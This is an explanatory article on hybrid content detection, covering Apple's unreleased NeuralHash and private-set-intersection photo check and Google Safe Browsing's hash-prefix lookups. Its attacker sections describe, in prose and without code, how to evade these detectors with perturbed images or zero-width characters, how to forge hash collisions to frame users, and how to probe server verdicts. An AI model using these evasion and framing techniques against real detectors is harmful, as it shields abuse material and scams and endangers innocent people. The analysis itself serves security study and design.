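# Hybrid detection: on-device models that flag content and private server checks that confirm it

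## What a two-stage check is and who attacks it

In a two-stage check for harmful content, software on the user's phone or computer makes a provisional finding and a server makes the final one. The content may be a photo on its way to cloud storage, a web page that imitates a bank's, or a text message. The local model, a small classifier or hash function on the device, examines each item and flags any that look harmful. The device then sends some information about the flagged item to the operator's servers. The server check, which uses a larger model or a list that users never receive, confirms or rejects the flag, and this decision is called the verdict.

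Apple (2021) published a design of this kind for finding known images of child sexual abuse among photos about to be uploaded to its iCloud storage. Google runs one in its Chrome browser against scams and phishing pages (fake login pages that collect passwords). Someone browsing the web normally wants the warning, so the adversary is whoever built the page. In Apple's design, the adversary may be the phone's owner.

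### Why part of the detector sits on the device

The usual reason for checking on the device first is privacy, since most items never have to leave the device to be checked. An operator can also check material its servers cannot read, such as end-to-end encrypted messages, which only the sender and recipient can read. In *SoK*, a survey of attacks on AI models in phones, Huang, Zheng and colleagues (2026) add that local models answer faster and work offline. A two-stage check keeps only part of that benefit, because a flag is provisional until the server replies.

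Whether the user gains privacy depends on what the local model is compared with. Using a local model reveals less than having a server read everything. But *Bugs in our Pockets* (Abelson, Anderson and colleagues, 2021), a critique by fourteen security researchers, argues that a scanner on the device, unlike one on a server, can reach files the owner never meant to share with anyone.

Some threats are also easier to detect on the device. Bawa, Lim and Lu (2025) report in *Using AI to stop tech support scams in Chrome* that the average malicious site exists for less than ten minutes, so many are gone before Google's crawlers arrive. Some sites also show crawlers a harmless version. The browser has the version shown to the user, while the user is viewing it.

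The second stage runs on a server because phones have limited memory and computing power, and because a single phone cannot compare content across millions of accounts, as spam filters do. Some of the lists used for matching are also too sensitive to distribute to phones. Abelson and colleagues cite Neal Krawetz, who showed that hashes from PhotoDNA, Microsoft's image-matching system, can be turned back into 26-by-26-pixel thumbnails of the original images, which are sometimes detailed enough to identify a person. Recovering thumbnails from a list of abuse-image hashes would harm the victims again.

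### Why the local weights count as public

Attackers can run the same software that ships to users on their own machines and study it for as long as they like, so they don't need a victim's phone. For example, Chrome by default downloads the language model behind its scam detection to desktop computers as a multi-gigabyte file called weights.bin (Android Authority, *Google weighs in on Chrome's weights.bin controversy*, 2026).

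Agyemang, Asante and colleagues (*Harvesting Apple's Orchard*, 2026) collected 1,137 model files from Apple's operating systems, including text message filters, and found that 368 exposed their learned parameters without encryption. Their test for readable weights was generous, and a stricter version cuts the number of separate weight files that pass from 281 to 238. They also converted 155 compiled models, whose format has no public decompiler, back into a form that ordinary tools can load and run.

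Encrypting the model file delays an attacker, but the device has to decrypt the model to run it, and Huang and colleagues describe tools that copy it out of memory at that point. *Protecting On-Device AI Inference* (2026), a review of such attacks, cites one automated tool that reused the models in 1,250 of 1,511 popular apps. But the review also reports that the more advanced extraction methods, which read memory or side effects such as power use, often fail outside the laboratory. Custom encryption and unusual software formats make extraction even harder.

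These obstacles matter less than they seem to, because once one person overcomes them, anyone can use the result. Outsiders took barely two weeks to reverse-engineer the copy of NeuralHash, Apple's hash function for photos, that was already in iOS 14. *What does the NeuralHash collision mean?*, a post by the engineer Eric Rescorla on the blog Educated Guesswork, concludes that designers should expect such an algorithm to become known eventually unless the operator makes a real effort to conceal it.

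The standard assumption is therefore a white-box attacker, someone who has the local model's weights and can run and analyse it without limit. This attacker can use the weights to compute a gradient, which shows how small changes to an image would move the model's score, and follow it until the score crosses the threshold. Models on phones usually come in a format that can run but can't compute gradients, but Huang and colleagues describe a tool that restores this ability. Most scammers will never go to this trouble, but designers plan for a white-box attacker because a design that withstands one will also withstand a less determined attacker.

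### One item, from score to action

Suppose a user opens a page that imitates a bank's login screen, and the local model gives scores from 0 to 1. The numbers are invented, but the sequence of steps is general.

1. The local model examines the page and gives it a score of 0.72.
2. The software compares the score with a threshold that the operator chose in advance, say 0.60. The page is over it, which makes a flag. A page with a score of 0.55 would go no further.
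3. The device sends data about the flagged page. Depending on the design, this may be the address, a set of measurements, a summary of the text or an encrypted record.
4. The server check weighs that data together with whatever else the operator holds, such as the site's history, and reaches a verdict.
5. Something happens, or nothing does. The browser may show a warning. In other systems the operator blocks an upload, passes the case to human reviewers or reports the user.

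Rahalkar and Virgaonkar (2022) note in *SoK*, a survey of moderation in encrypted services, that some systems also let users appeal. Designs differ in the middle steps. In Apple's design, the phone could not tell whether a photo had matched, and the server could not read any matches until the account reached a set number of them.

The server receives only the items that the local model flags, unless the operator also samples unflagged ones. It can overturn a flag, but it cannot catch a bad item that the local model missed and never sent. An attacker therefore has to fool only the local model to hide a bad item, but must also fool the server to get a harmless one condemned.

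### Counting the errors

A false positive is a harmless item that the detector reports as bad, and a false negative is a bad item that it misses. *Draft amendments to Illegal content Codes of Practice for search services* (2026), from the UK's communications regulator, Ofcom, defines recall as the share of the target content analysed that the technology detects, and precision as the share of detected content that is target content.

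Suppose 100 of 10,000 pages are phishing, and a local model flags 300 pages, including 95 of the phishing pages. Its recall is 95% and its precision is about 32%. It wrongly flags only about 2% of the harmless pages, but about two in three flags are wrong because harmless pages are so much more common. If the server then confirms 90 of the 95 correct flags and 2 of the 205 mistaken ones, users see 92 warnings, of which 90 are correct. Precision rises to about 98% and recall falls to 90%.

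Chrome's developers say they aim for roughly this trade-off. In *How visual model in client-side detection works?*, Hoang Nguyen Dai (2025) asked on their mailing list whether either of the browser's phishing models could be enough on its own to classify a page as phishing. Daniel Rubery replied that neither could, because the local models use little compute and are tuned for high recall, while the server provides the precision needed for a warning.

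Abelson and colleagues point out that messaging services carry billions of messages a day, so even one false positive in a thousand would leave millions for central assessment. Under Ofcom's draft, which concerns intimate images shared without consent, large search services should balance precision against recall, record how they struck the balance and review it at least every six months. One factor they must consider is how well their systems catch false positives afterwards, so a strong second stage can justify a looser first one.

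### Hashes and classifiers

A hash is a short code computed from a file. With a cryptographic hash, changing a single pixel gives a completely different code, so two files with the same code are, for practical purposes, identical. This kind of hash reliably detects exact copies but misses pictures that have been cropped or re-saved.

A perceptual hash gives the same or similar codes to images that look alike. Ofcom's *Overview of Perceptual Hashing Technology* (2022) describes a simple one. The software converts the picture to greyscale, shrinks it and divides it into a five-by-five grid. Each square becomes a 1 or a 0 depending on whether it is brighter or darker than the average, and the 25 digits in sequence are the hash. To compare an image *s* with a list *D* of known hashes, the software measures the distance *d* between codes, for instance the share of digits that differ. There is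 a match if some *h* in *D* satisfies *d*(*H*(*s*), *h*) ≤ ε, where *H* is the hash function and ε the tolerance. A larger ε catches more altered copies but also more innocent pictures. NeuralHash allows no tolerance at the comparison stage, so the codes must be equal.

Such a hash measures how similar whole images look, regardless of whether they show the same object. In Ofcom's example, two very similar photos of different hamburgers may match, but two very different photos of the same hamburger should not. A collision occurs when two visibly different images have the same hash, or nearly the same one.

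A classifier is trained on examples to estimate whether an item belongs to a category, so it can recognise an abusive image or a scam page that nobody has listed. It can also be wrong about a far wider range of items. The two methods overlap in practice. NeuralHash compares images with a list, as any perceptual hash does, but it uses a neural network to compute the code, so the gradient methods that work against classifiers also work against it. Definitions also vary. Ofcom's 2022 overview counts NeuralHash as a perceptual hash, whereas its 2026 draft excludes technology that uses machine learning to compare similarity.

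### Who attacks the check

It helps to sort attackers by what they want, since the same knowledge of the local model serves opposite ends.

| Attacker | Aim | Holds | Sees |
|---|---|---|---|
| Evader | Get a bad item past the check | The item and the local model | The local score of every version they try |
| Framer | Get an innocent user flagged | The local model, a target to imitate, a way to reach the victim | The local score, and seldom the verdict on the victim |
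| Flooder | Overload the servers or the reviewers | The framer's tools and many accounts or recipients | The local score, and perhaps signs of delay |
| Prober | Learn how the server check decides | The local model, test accounts, a supply of flagged items | Whatever the system reveals of each verdict |
| Operator or government | Search for content beyond the stated purpose | The server check, the list and the update channel | Everything the devices send in readable form |

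An evader can test changes to the content in private. *Double Down on Defense* (2026), a study of perceptual hashes built on neural networks, counts an evasion as successful when the original image matched its reference and a slightly altered copy no longer does. Abelson and colleagues cite an experiment by Shubham Jain and others in which nearly imperceptible changes hid 99.9% of the images from detection. Cruder changes can also work. When Agyemang and colleagues inserted zero-width spaces, which take up no room on the screen, into 20 messages, Apple's US-English message filter changed its label for 14. The sample is small, and the test used a stand-in for one component of the real filter.

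The input to a content detector is often a page or message that the attacker wrote. Huang and colleagues regard attacker control over a model's input as a demanding assumption, because phone users normally choose what their own models examine. That reasoning is sound for a camera app that diagnoses skin conditions, but not for a content detector. An evader who owns the device can also tamper with the local model.

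A framer needs a forced false flag, meaning a harmless-looking item that the victim will keep or upload, altered so that the local model flags it. Rescorla notes that with a hash list this takes more knowledge than evasion does, since the framer needs at least one hash on the list as well as the algorithm. But anyone who has a listed image can compute its hash, so keeping the list secret only partly protects against framing. Within 48 hours after NeuralHash's code was published, anonymous experimenters had made images with the same hashes as chosen targets and released a toolkit for making more.

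A flooder can use the same toolkit to produce forced false flags in bulk. These flags only have to take up human reviewers' time, even if they don't fool anyone. A flood can also provide cover for an evader. *Media Integrity and Authentication* (Young, Vaughan and colleagues, 2026), a Microsoft report on verifying where images and recordings come from, describes a similar attack on verification services and suggests that an attacker might want to disable the service just before a disinformation campaign.

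A prober tries to learn how the server check behaves, since that half of the system is not on the device. Any response that varies with the verdict, even whether a warning appears, is a probing oracle, because the attacker can submit an item, note the result, change the item and try again. For this reason, Young and colleagues advise against opening watermark detectors to the public without extra safeguards. In 2021, Abelson and colleagues knew of one real defence for models on a server, which was to monitor queries and cut off any sequence that looked like attempted extraction. The results of probing are useful mainly to evaders and framers.

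The operator is a potential attacker because users cannot inspect the hidden part of the system. A government could order the company to add political images to a list of abuse images, and a bribed employee or an intruder could add them without an order. Outsiders would have trouble noticing, since the law in many countries forbids them to possess the material they would need to check the list. Apple's answer was to accept only entries supplied by child-safety organisations in at least two separate jurisdictions, with human review as a further safeguard. Abelson and colleagues were not persuaded that any such arrangement could withstand a determined state.

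### What the designer has to decide

The designer first decides what runs on the device and what runs on the server, because everything placed on the device becomes public. The next decision is how many bad items the local model may miss, which the server cannot correct, and how many false flags the server and its reviewers can handle. The designer then decides whether the device receives the verdict. A browser needs it to warn the user, but a photo service can withhold it from the phone, which gives anyone probing the system less information. Finally, the designer decides what data the server receives. More data improves the verdicts but reduces the user's privacy, although cryptographic protocols can limit that loss.

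Since Auguste Kerckhoffs wrote on military ciphers in 1883, security engineers have held that a system should stay secure even if the enemy knows its design, as long as the keys stay secret. A hidden server model fits this rule badly because an operator can replace a leaked key quickly but may have to retrain a leaked model. The operator also may not find out that someone has copied the model's behaviour by probing it.

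## Splitting a photo check between phone and server: Apple's 2021 design

Apple's check would have applied only to photos being uploaded to iCloud Photos, so a phone with that service switched off would have hashed nothing. Any other phone would have sent Apple's servers an encrypted record of every photo it uploaded, whether or not the photo matched the list. The flag would have existed only inside that record, where the phone could not read it. The servers could have opened the records of matching photos only after the account had passed a set number of matches.

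Apple never deployed the system, but it published much of the design. Caudill (2021) complained that the company's 12-page technical summary left some important details poorly defined or undefined. The cryptography is much better documented, because *The Apple PSI System* (Bhowmick, Boneh and colleagues, 2021) sets out the whole protocol with proofs.

### Where the list comes from

In the United States, the National Center for Missing and Exploited Children (NCMEC) is the only non-governmental organisation that may legally possess abuse images. Apple therefore could not compute the hashes itself and relied on NCMEC and similar organisations to supply them. Apple also could not look at the images, so it assumed that a list might contain harmless pictures, either by mistake or because someone had pressured the organisation supplying it.

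To protect against this, Apple required every entry to come from two jurisdictions. If one organisation submits hashes *a*, *b*, *c* and *d*, and another in a different country submits *b*, *d* and *e*, the list contains only *b* and *d*. But the rule also excludes genuine abuse images that only one organisation knows about.

Apple planned to build the list into the operating system and ship the same copy to everyone. It would also publish a root hash, a single cryptographic hash computed from the whole encrypted list, which users could compare with the one shown on their phones. Auditors could visit Apple and check that the list contained only hashes the organisations had in common.

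In Educated Guesswork's *More on Apple's Client-side CSAM Scanning* (CSAM is child sexual abuse material), Eric Rescorla found the reasoning sound but thought it gave only weak assurance. A compromised phone could display the wrong root hash. Two governments could also agree to add each other's images, perhaps through an existing intelligence alliance such as Five Eyes, which has five English-speaking members. An audit would not catch this, because the images would be on both lists.

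The matching works the same way whatever the listed images show. Rescorla wrote in an earlier post on Educated Guesswork that Apple could find everyone who had copied *Everydays*, a digital artwork by Beeple, just by adding it to the list.

### How NeuralHash turns a photo into 96 bits

Struppek, Hintersdorf and colleagues (2021), in *Learning to Break Deep Perceptual Hashing*, extracted NeuralHash from a Mac and described how it works.

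1. The software shrinks the photo to 360 by 360 pixels and rescales its colour values to lie between −1 and 1.
2. A neural network with 1.8 million parameters turns the result into a list of 128 numbers. The network is a modified MobileNetV3, a compact design suited to phones.
3. The software multiplies this list by a fixed table of 128 by 96 numbers, which gives 96 new numbers.
4. Each positive number becomes a 1 and each negative number a 0. These 96 digits are the photo's NeuralHash.

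The 128 numbers can be thought of as the coordinates of a point. Each column of the table defines a hyperplane, a flat boundary that divides the space in two. Each digit records which side of one boundary the point is on.

An example with two coordinates and one boundary shows how editing a photo can affect its digit. Let the photo's point be (0.8, 0.3) and the column be (1, −2). The result is 0.8 − 0.6 = 0.2, so the digit is 1. A slightly cropped copy at (0.8, 0.35) gives 0.1, so the digit is still 1. A more heavily edited copy at (0.8, 0.45) gives −0.1, so the digit changes to 0.

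That one change would prevent a match. Leblanc-Albarel and Preneel, in *Breaking Widely Deployed Perceptual Hash Functions* (2026), take Apple's documents to mean that near matches also counted. But the published protocol cannot detect near matches, so tolerance for edits must come entirely from the network.

Apple trained the network for this by contrastive learning, which moves the points for an image and an altered copy of it closer together and moves the points for two different images apart. According to *Expanded Protections for Children* (2021), the document Apple released at launch, a photo keeps the same hash after slight cropping, resizing or conversion to black and white.

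The Eclectic Light Company's *How Apple intends checking images for CSAM* (2021) described NeuralHash's training pairs as including abuse images. A few days later, Apple said it had not trained NeuralHash on any such images.

### Comparing hashes without revealing them

The phone must not learn what is on the list, and Apple must not learn the hashes of photos that aren't on it. Private set intersection (PSI) protocols address this problem by letting two parties find the items they have in common while learning little or nothing else. Many need several rounds of messages, but Apple wanted to send the list once, in a software update, and have the phone reply with one short message per photo, so Bhowmick and colleagues designed a new variant.

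It relies on elliptic curves, which are sets of points that can be added together. Multiplying a point by a secret number is easy, but nobody knows a practical way to recover the number from the result. The same steps work with whole numbers if you replace each result with its remainder after division by 101. This version is easier to follow, but it gives no secrecy because anyone can recover the number by dividing.

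1. Apple chooses a secret number α, here 7. It takes a public starting value *G*, here 5, and publishes *L* = α*G* = 35.
2. Apple converts each hash on the list into a value *H*(*x*). For one listed image this is 20. Apple multiplies it by α to get 140, which leaves a remainder of 39, and puts *P* = 39 in the table that goes to every phone. This step is called blinding, because a phone that sees 39 but doesn't know α cannot get back to 20.
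3. The phone hashes a new photo and converts the hash in the same way into *H*(*y*). It picks two fresh random numbers, β = 3 and γ = 4, and computes *Q* = β*H*(*y*) + γ*G* and *S* = β*P* + γ*L*.
4. The phone uses *S* as a key to encrypt part of its message. It sends *Q* to the server and keeps *S* to itself.
5. The server multiplies *Q* by α and tries the result as the key.

If the photo is the listed one, *H*(*y*) is 20 and *Q* is 80. *S* is 257, which leaves 55. The server computes 7 × 80 = 560, which also leaves 55, so the key works. If the photo is a different one with *H*(*y*) = 21, *S* still leaves 55 but *Q* is 83. The server computes 7 × 83 = 581, which leaves 76, so the key fails.

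α*Q* equals *S* exactly when *P* = α*H*(*y*), which means the photo's hash is the one in that cell. Because β and γ are random, a failed attempt gives the server no information about the photo's hash.

The real table has a cell for every listed hash and some spare cells, which Apple fills with random points. A phone can't tell the spare cells from the others. For each photo, the phone calculates two cells where a matching entry could be, makes an encrypted key for each and sends the keys in random order. The server can open exactly one of them if the photo is on the list, and neither if it isn't.

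This arrangement, called a cuckoo table, has no room for a small fraction of the listed hashes, which Apple leaves out. Bhowmick and colleagues accept these misses because each update of the list would omit a different random selection.

### The safety voucher and the match threshold

With each photo, the phone sends a message called a safety voucher, which has two layers of encryption. If the photo matches, the server can remove the outer layer. This reveals a piece of a second key, called the account key here, and a package that only the account key can open. The package contains the photo's NeuralHash and a visual derivative, such as a low-resolution copy of the photo. The phone creates one account key for all of the user's photos and never sends it whole.

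The phone divides the account key by threshold secret sharing, a method that splits a secret into shares so that anyone with a set number of them can rebuild it, while anyone with fewer learns nothing about it. Suppose the key is 42 and the server needs three shares. The phone chooses a random parabola that has the value 42 at *x* = 0, for example *f*(*x*) = 42 + 3*x* + 2*x*². Each voucher contains one point on the curve, such as (1, 47), (2, 56) or (3, 69). Three points determine a parabola, so a server with three vouchers can calculate *f*(0) and get the key. With only two points, the server can fit a parabola to every possible key, so it cannot tell which key is correct.

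Apple's launch document gives the example of a secret split into a thousand shares, any ten of which can rebuild it. But it also requires the number of shares to exceed the threshold, which would mean eleven. The protocol paper consistently requires *t* + 1 shares for a threshold of *t*, so with a threshold of 30, the server can open the contents at the 31st match.

If a user has the same photo on a phone and a tablet, it counts once, because both devices have the same keys and calculate the same share from the photo's identifier. But if the user imports the photo again from a USB drive, the copy gets a new identifier and counts a second time. Bhowmick and colleagues write that a mechanism outside the protocol deals with this, but they don't describe it.

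### Hiding the number of matches

With the design described so far, the server could count the vouchers whose outer layer it can remove. That count would reveal, for example, that an account had two matches, long before it reached the threshold. To prevent this, the phone randomly replaces some vouchers with synthetic ones. The server can always remove the outer layer of a synthetic voucher, but the voucher contains only a dummy share and a package of encrypted zeros.

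Suppose the server again needs three real shares, and the user uploads five photos. Photos 2 and 4 are on the list, and the phone has made photo 5's voucher synthetic. The server can open the outer layer of vouchers 2, 4 and 5. This reveals that photos 1 and 3 don't match, but not which of the other three vouchers are real. The server can't recover the key because only two of the three shares are real.

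The user then uploads photo 6, which is also on the list. The server now has three real shares and a dummy. To let the server tell them apart, every voucher also carries a point. In an example this small, the points in all the real vouchers lie on one straight line that the phone chose at random, and the point in a synthetic voucher is random. Any two points lie on some line, so the server can't identify the real vouchers when there are only two. Three points are very unlikely to line up by chance, so the server can now pick out vouchers 2, 4 and 6, which also shows that voucher 5 is synthetic. It then rebuilds the account key and opens the three derivatives. With a higher threshold, the phone uses curves instead of a line, and the server finds the real vouchers by solving a set of linear equations.

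| Stage | What the phone learns | What the server learns |
|---|---|---|
| The list arrives in an update | Roughly how many hashes it contains | Nothing new, since Apple built the list |
| The phone makes a voucher | The photo's NeuralHash and whether the voucher is synthetic, but not whether the photo matches | Nothing |
| The server tests the outer layer | Nothing | The photo's identifier, and whether the photo is a possible match |
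| The account is below the threshold | Nothing | A set of possible matches in which real and synthetic ones look the same |
| The account passes the threshold | Nothing | Which vouchers are real matches, and their NeuralHashes and derivatives |
| Apple checks the derivatives | Nothing, unless Apple disables the account | Whether the second hash and the reviewers confirm the matches |

Apple overstated slightly when it wrote that its servers would learn nothing about any of a user's photos below the threshold. The server does learn that most of them aren't on the list, and it has an upper limit on the number that are. Synthetic vouchers also cause some missed detections, because a match never counts if the phone happens to replace that photo's voucher.

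The phone never learns whether a photo matched, because a user who could see matches could add test images and work out what was on the list. Bhowmick and colleagues sketch proofs that neither side can learn more than the protocol intends. In a separate analysis, the cryptographer Mihir Bellare reached the same conclusions for the version without synthetic vouchers.

The proofs leave two gaps. They protect the user only with respect to the list actually in the table, and a dishonest operator could put extra hashes in the spare cells. An auditor who knew both the list and the table could rule this out, but Apple relied on measures outside the protocol. The proofs also don't guarantee a correct result if someone modifies the phone's software, because that person can hold photos back or report matches that don't exist.

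### Apple's tests and the threshold of 30

Apple compared 100 million photos that were not abuse images with the hashes from NCMEC's collection and found three false matches. It found none in a separate test of about 500,000 images of adult pornography. To set the threshold, Apple assumed a higher rate of one false match per million photos. At that rate, it expected that with a threshold of 30 matches, an innocent account would have less than a one in a trillion chance of passing it, even if its photo library were larger than any that existed.

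Apple described its assumed rate of one in a million as including a safety margin of two orders of magnitude, or a factor of 100. The assumed rate is about 33 times the measured rate, which is still a wide margin.

The test on adult images was too small to show that the false-match rate for adult pornography is below the assumed one in a million. If the true rate were six in a million, a test of 500,000 images would still find no false matches about one time in twenty. Adult images are probably also among the harmless photos for which false matches matter most, because a reviewer looking at a small, blurred copy could mistake one for abuse.

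These figures are for photos that nobody had altered to cause a match. Rescorla noted that a threshold based on them does not protect against someone who deliberately makes matching images.

### The second hash on the server

Once an account passes the threshold, the server opens only the derivatives of the matching photos. The vouchers don't contain a key to the full photos, and the server can't request copies from the phone. Before any person sees the derivatives, the server computes a second perceptual hash of each one and compares it with the hashes of known abuse images.

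The one purpose Apple gave for the second hash was to reject harmless images that someone had "adversarially perturbed to cause false NeuralHash matches" and that had taken the account past the threshold. The derivatives would go to human reviewers only if the second hash confirmed the finding.

Apple did not mention the second hash at launch. Its launch document describes manual review as the next step after the threshold. The second hash appears in the threat model that Apple released on 13 August 2021, about a week after the announcement. MacRumors' *Apple Outlines Security and Privacy of CSAM Detection System in New Document* covered the threat model that day. Five days later, when outsiders were already testing NeuralHash, Apple told the news site Motherboard that the second algorithm was not public and would run on Apple's servers after an account passed 30 matches (iphonewalle, 2021).

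Apple never published the algorithm, its error rate, the length of its hashes or how close two hashes had to be to match. It also didn't specify how many of an account's derivatives had to match before reviewers saw them. Apple called the hash independent but didn't explain how it had tested this. The protection depends on that independence, because an image that fools one function is more likely to fool the other if both respond to similar features.

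It is also unclear where the reference hashes would have come from. Rescorla points out that Apple never receives the abuse images, so the organisations would have to send it either derivatives of the images or finished hashes.

The second hash can keep forged matches away from the reviewers, but it comes too late to do everything a server check might do. False matches still count towards the threshold, and the server has already opened the derivatives by the time the second hash rejects them.

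The server check also relies on the phone to make the derivative it examines, so a modified phone could attach a picture of a garden to the voucher for an abuse image. NeuralHash would match, but the second hash would presumably reject the match. A server check that received the photo itself would not have this weakness, although someone who can modify the phone could avoid detection more simply by, for example, switching off iCloud Photos.

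Rescorla argues that the second hash must be secret as well as independent, because otherwise an attacker could make an image that matches both hashes. He considers the second hash less exposed than NeuralHash because it doesn't run on phones. If it leaked, Apple could replace it and ask the organisations to recompute their hashes, without a software update for users.

But a dishonest operator could also exploit the hidden stage. Rescorla describes how Apple could put every country's banned images in the one worldwide list, then use the second hash and a separate list for each country to decide which matches to pursue. Every user would have the same list and root hash, so none of the checks on the phone would detect this.

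### Human review and the report

Apple's reviewers would look at the derivatives and decide whether they showed child sexual abuse. They would not check whether a photo was the same as a listed image, since Apple had no copies of the listed images. Apple presented this as a safeguard. If someone added a political image to the list, the reviewer would see that it wasn't an abuse image, leave the account alone and refer the case to Apple's engineers. Such an addition could harm someone only if the reviewers were also told which harmless images to report, and complied.

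No report would go out automatically. If the reviewers confirmed the finding, they would disable the account and report the user to a child-safety organisation. In the United States, this is NCMEC, which works with law enforcement. A user who thought Apple had made a mistake could appeal to have the account reinstated.

Reviewers check the software's matches before an account is reported, and they can only report accounts that have passed the threshold. This protects against a careless or corrupt reviewer. It is a less convincing protection against pressure on Apple itself, which runs the servers and employs the reviewers. Apple promised to refuse any request to add other images or to report anything else.

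Because reviewers work from derivatives, the system is also easier to extend. Apple's software chief, Craig Federighi, said the check was only part of the process of storing photos in iCloud. Rescorla replied that reviewers don't need the uploaded photo, so Apple could scan pictures that never leave the phone with fairly modest changes. Apple chose to limit the check to iCloud photos, and the cryptography did not enforce that limit.

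### What happened to the design

Apple planned to release the system by the end of 2021 but postponed it, citing feedback from customers, advocacy groups and researchers. It abandoned the plan in December 2022 (MacRumors, *Apple Abandons Controversial Plans to Detect Known CSAM in iCloud Photos*, 2022).

Apple kept another feature from the same announcement. The current version of its *Expanded Protections for Children* describes software that warns children about images containing nudity. The software runs entirely on the device and sends no sign of a detection to Apple or parents. A false flag causes an unnecessary warning, so the design doesn't need a second stage.

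Leblanc-Albarel and Preneel, who found unaltered photos of different people with the same NeuralHash value, report that the function is still on all Apple devices even though the plan has ended, and that Apple has not disclosed what it is for. A new version appears to have reached Macs in early 2024, also without explanation.

European Union negotiators had provisionally excluded end-to-end encrypted messages from planned rules on detecting abuse material. Reuter (2026) reports in *Zivilgesellschaft warnt vor Ausweitung der Überwachung* that the Council presidency now wants to remove the explicit protection for these messages from the rules on voluntary scanning. Reuter adds that the German bar association warns this could allow scanning on devices.

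## Checking web addresses against a local list or a server list

Google Safe Browsing provides the phishing and malware warnings in Chrome, Firefox and Safari. For years it worked as a two-stage check without a trained model. The browser held a list of shortened hashes of dangerous addresses and contacted Google's servers only when an address matched one of them. Because both stages looked for exact matches, anyone could calculate the error rate from the length of the list, whereas Apple had to measure NeuralHash's error rate on millions of photos.

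In March 2024 Google changed Chrome's default so that the browser checks each address against the server's list unless it has already identified the address as probably safe. Google made the change because the lists on users' devices were going out of date faster than it could replace them.

### From an address to a hash prefix

A scammer can write the same address in many ways, and each spelling has a different cryptographic hash. The browser therefore puts the address into a standard form before hashing it. Under the rules in Google's *URLs and Hashing*, it deletes everything after a # sign, decodes characters written as percent codes, converts the host name to lower case and removes sequences such as `/../` from the path.

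An entry on Google's list may cover a whole site, one folder or a single page, so the browser has to test all three. It combines up to five versions of the host name with up to six versions of the path, which gives at most 30 strings. It then computes a 32-byte hash of each string with SHA-256, a standard cryptographic hash function, and takes the first four bytes, called the hash prefix.

Suppose a user opens `A.Example.com/account/%6Cogin.html?id=7#top`, and Google has listed all of `a.example.com` as a phishing site. The listing is invented, but the hash is real and comes from Google's *Local Database*.

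1. The browser rewrites the address as `a.example.com/account/login.html?id=7`, since %6C is a code for the letter l.
2. It combines two hosts, `a.example.com` and `example.com`, with four paths: `/account/login.html?id=7`, `/account/login.html`, `/account/` and `/`. This makes eight strings.
3. It hashes all eight. The hash of `a.example.com/` begins 291bc5421f1cd54d and continues for another 24 bytes, so its prefix is 291bc542.
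4. It looks for the eight prefixes in the list on the device and finds 291bc542. This hit is the flag.
5. It sends 291bc542 to Google in a full-hash request. The server returns every full hash on its own list that begins with those four bytes, which is usually just one.
6. It compares all 32 bytes. If they agree, the user sees a warning. If the server's hash begins with 291bc542 but then differs, the hit was an accident and the page opens normally.

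The browser makes the final comparison itself, so it always knows the verdict.

If none of the eight prefixes is on the local list, the browser opens the page without contacting the server. This local check never misses an address that was on the list at the last update, because the browser stores a prefix for every listed address, whereas a trained model comes with no such guarantee. Educated Guesswork's *Can we make Safe Browsing safer?* explained in 2022 that the server can only cancel flags. Google can withdraw a mistaken entry immediately by returning no hash for its prefix, but a new site has to wait for the next update because the browser contacts the server only after a local hit.

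Exact matching is also easy to evade. A scammer can move the page to a new domain, which changes every string the browser checks, without knowing how the detector works. Adding a meaningless parameter to the end of the address doesn't help if the page itself is listed, because the browser also checks the path without parameters.

### How often a harmless address is flagged

A four-byte prefix has 32 bits, so there are 2³² (about 4.3 billion) possible prefixes. If the list has *N* entries, a harmless string matches one by accident with probability *p* = *N*/2³². If an address produces *k* strings, the probability of at least one accidental match is 1 − (1 − *p*)^*k*, which is close to *kp* when *p* is small.

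*A Privacy Analysis of Google and Yandex Safe Browsing* (Gerbet, Kumar and Lauradoux, 2015) counted about 630,000 prefixes in Google's malware and phishing lists. By 2022 there were about 3 million, according to Educated Guesswork. The last row of the table shows what would happen if the list grew to 5 million prefixes.

| Entries on the list | One string | Address with 8 strings | Address with 30 strings |
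|---|---|---|---|
| 630,000 | 1 in 6,800 | 1 in 850 | 1 in 230 |
| 3 million | 1 in 1,400 | 1 in 180 | 1 in 48 |
| 5 million | 1 in 860 | 1 in 110 | 1 in 29 |

Educated Guesswork also gives 1 in 1,400 for a single string, but its estimate of 1 in 400 to 1 in 200 for an address with five to ten strings is slightly too low. The formula gives 1 in 290 to 1 in 140.

These rates would be unacceptable if each hit caused a warning. Suppose one in 100,000 pages that people open is on a list of 3 million, and each address produces eight strings. For every correct hit there would be about 560 accidental ones, so the precision of the local stage would be under 0.2%. Comparing the full hashes removes almost all the accidental hits. The remaining false warnings are for harmless sites that Google listed by mistake.

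The hits are also unevenly spread. An address always has the same hash, so one that matches an entry by chance produces a hit for every visitor for as long as that entry is on the list. Attackers can also create prefix collisions deliberately, as *(Un)Safe Browsing* (Gerbet, Kumar and Lauradoux, 2014) describes.

Google accepts accidental hits because short prefixes save space. When Gerbet and colleagues stored the 2015 list in the compressed format that Chrome used, four-byte prefixes took up 1.3 megabytes and full hashes 19.1. Longer prefixes could make the server check unnecessary. Educated Guesswork calculates that with 80-bit prefixes and about a million entries, the probability of an accidental hit would be 2⁻⁶⁰, although resisting deliberate collisions would take more like 128 bits. In this design, the server check mainly makes up for the compression of the local list. The server has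 no better information about which sites are dangerous, except for any entries that Google has recently withdrawn.

### Why the list moved to the server

According to Google (2024), devices used to refresh their lists every 30 to 60 minutes. That was too slow for malicious sites, which last less than ten minutes on average.

Suppose a site lasts exactly ten minutes and receives visitors at a steady rate. Even if Google listed it the moment it appeared, a device that refreshes its local list every 30 minutes would have the new entry in time for only one visit in six. With a 60-minute refresh, the share would fall to one in twelve. In practice, Google also needs time to find the site, which makes the local list even less useful.

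According to Google's security blog, most unsafe sites last under ten minutes. Google's *Migration From V4* gives a figure of 60% of attack sites as of 2021. Both statements describe the typical site. The average lifetime could be much longer, because a few sites that survive for weeks would raise it, but the 60% figure is enough to support checking in real time.

A second reason for the change was that the list keeps growing, and some devices can't store all of it or download updates often enough. Keeping the list on the server avoids both problems.

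At launch, Li and Bawa (2024) forecast in *Browse safely with real-time protection on Chrome* that real-time checks would block 25% more phishing attempts. The migration guide attributes about 25–30% of missed phishing protection to out-of-date lists. If both figures describe the same improvement, the old check was blocking only about half of all attempts, because a quarter of the misses equals a quarter of the successes only when there are as many misses as successes. But Google doesn't say that the figures are comparable, and some of the expected gain may have come from the server's longer list.

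### The new order of checks

Chrome now first checks web addresses against the Global Cache, Google's list of sites that are probably safe. Google's *Real Time Mode* describes the procedure for programs that query Safe Browsing through version 5 of its API.

1. The browser standardises the address, forms the strings and hashes them as before.
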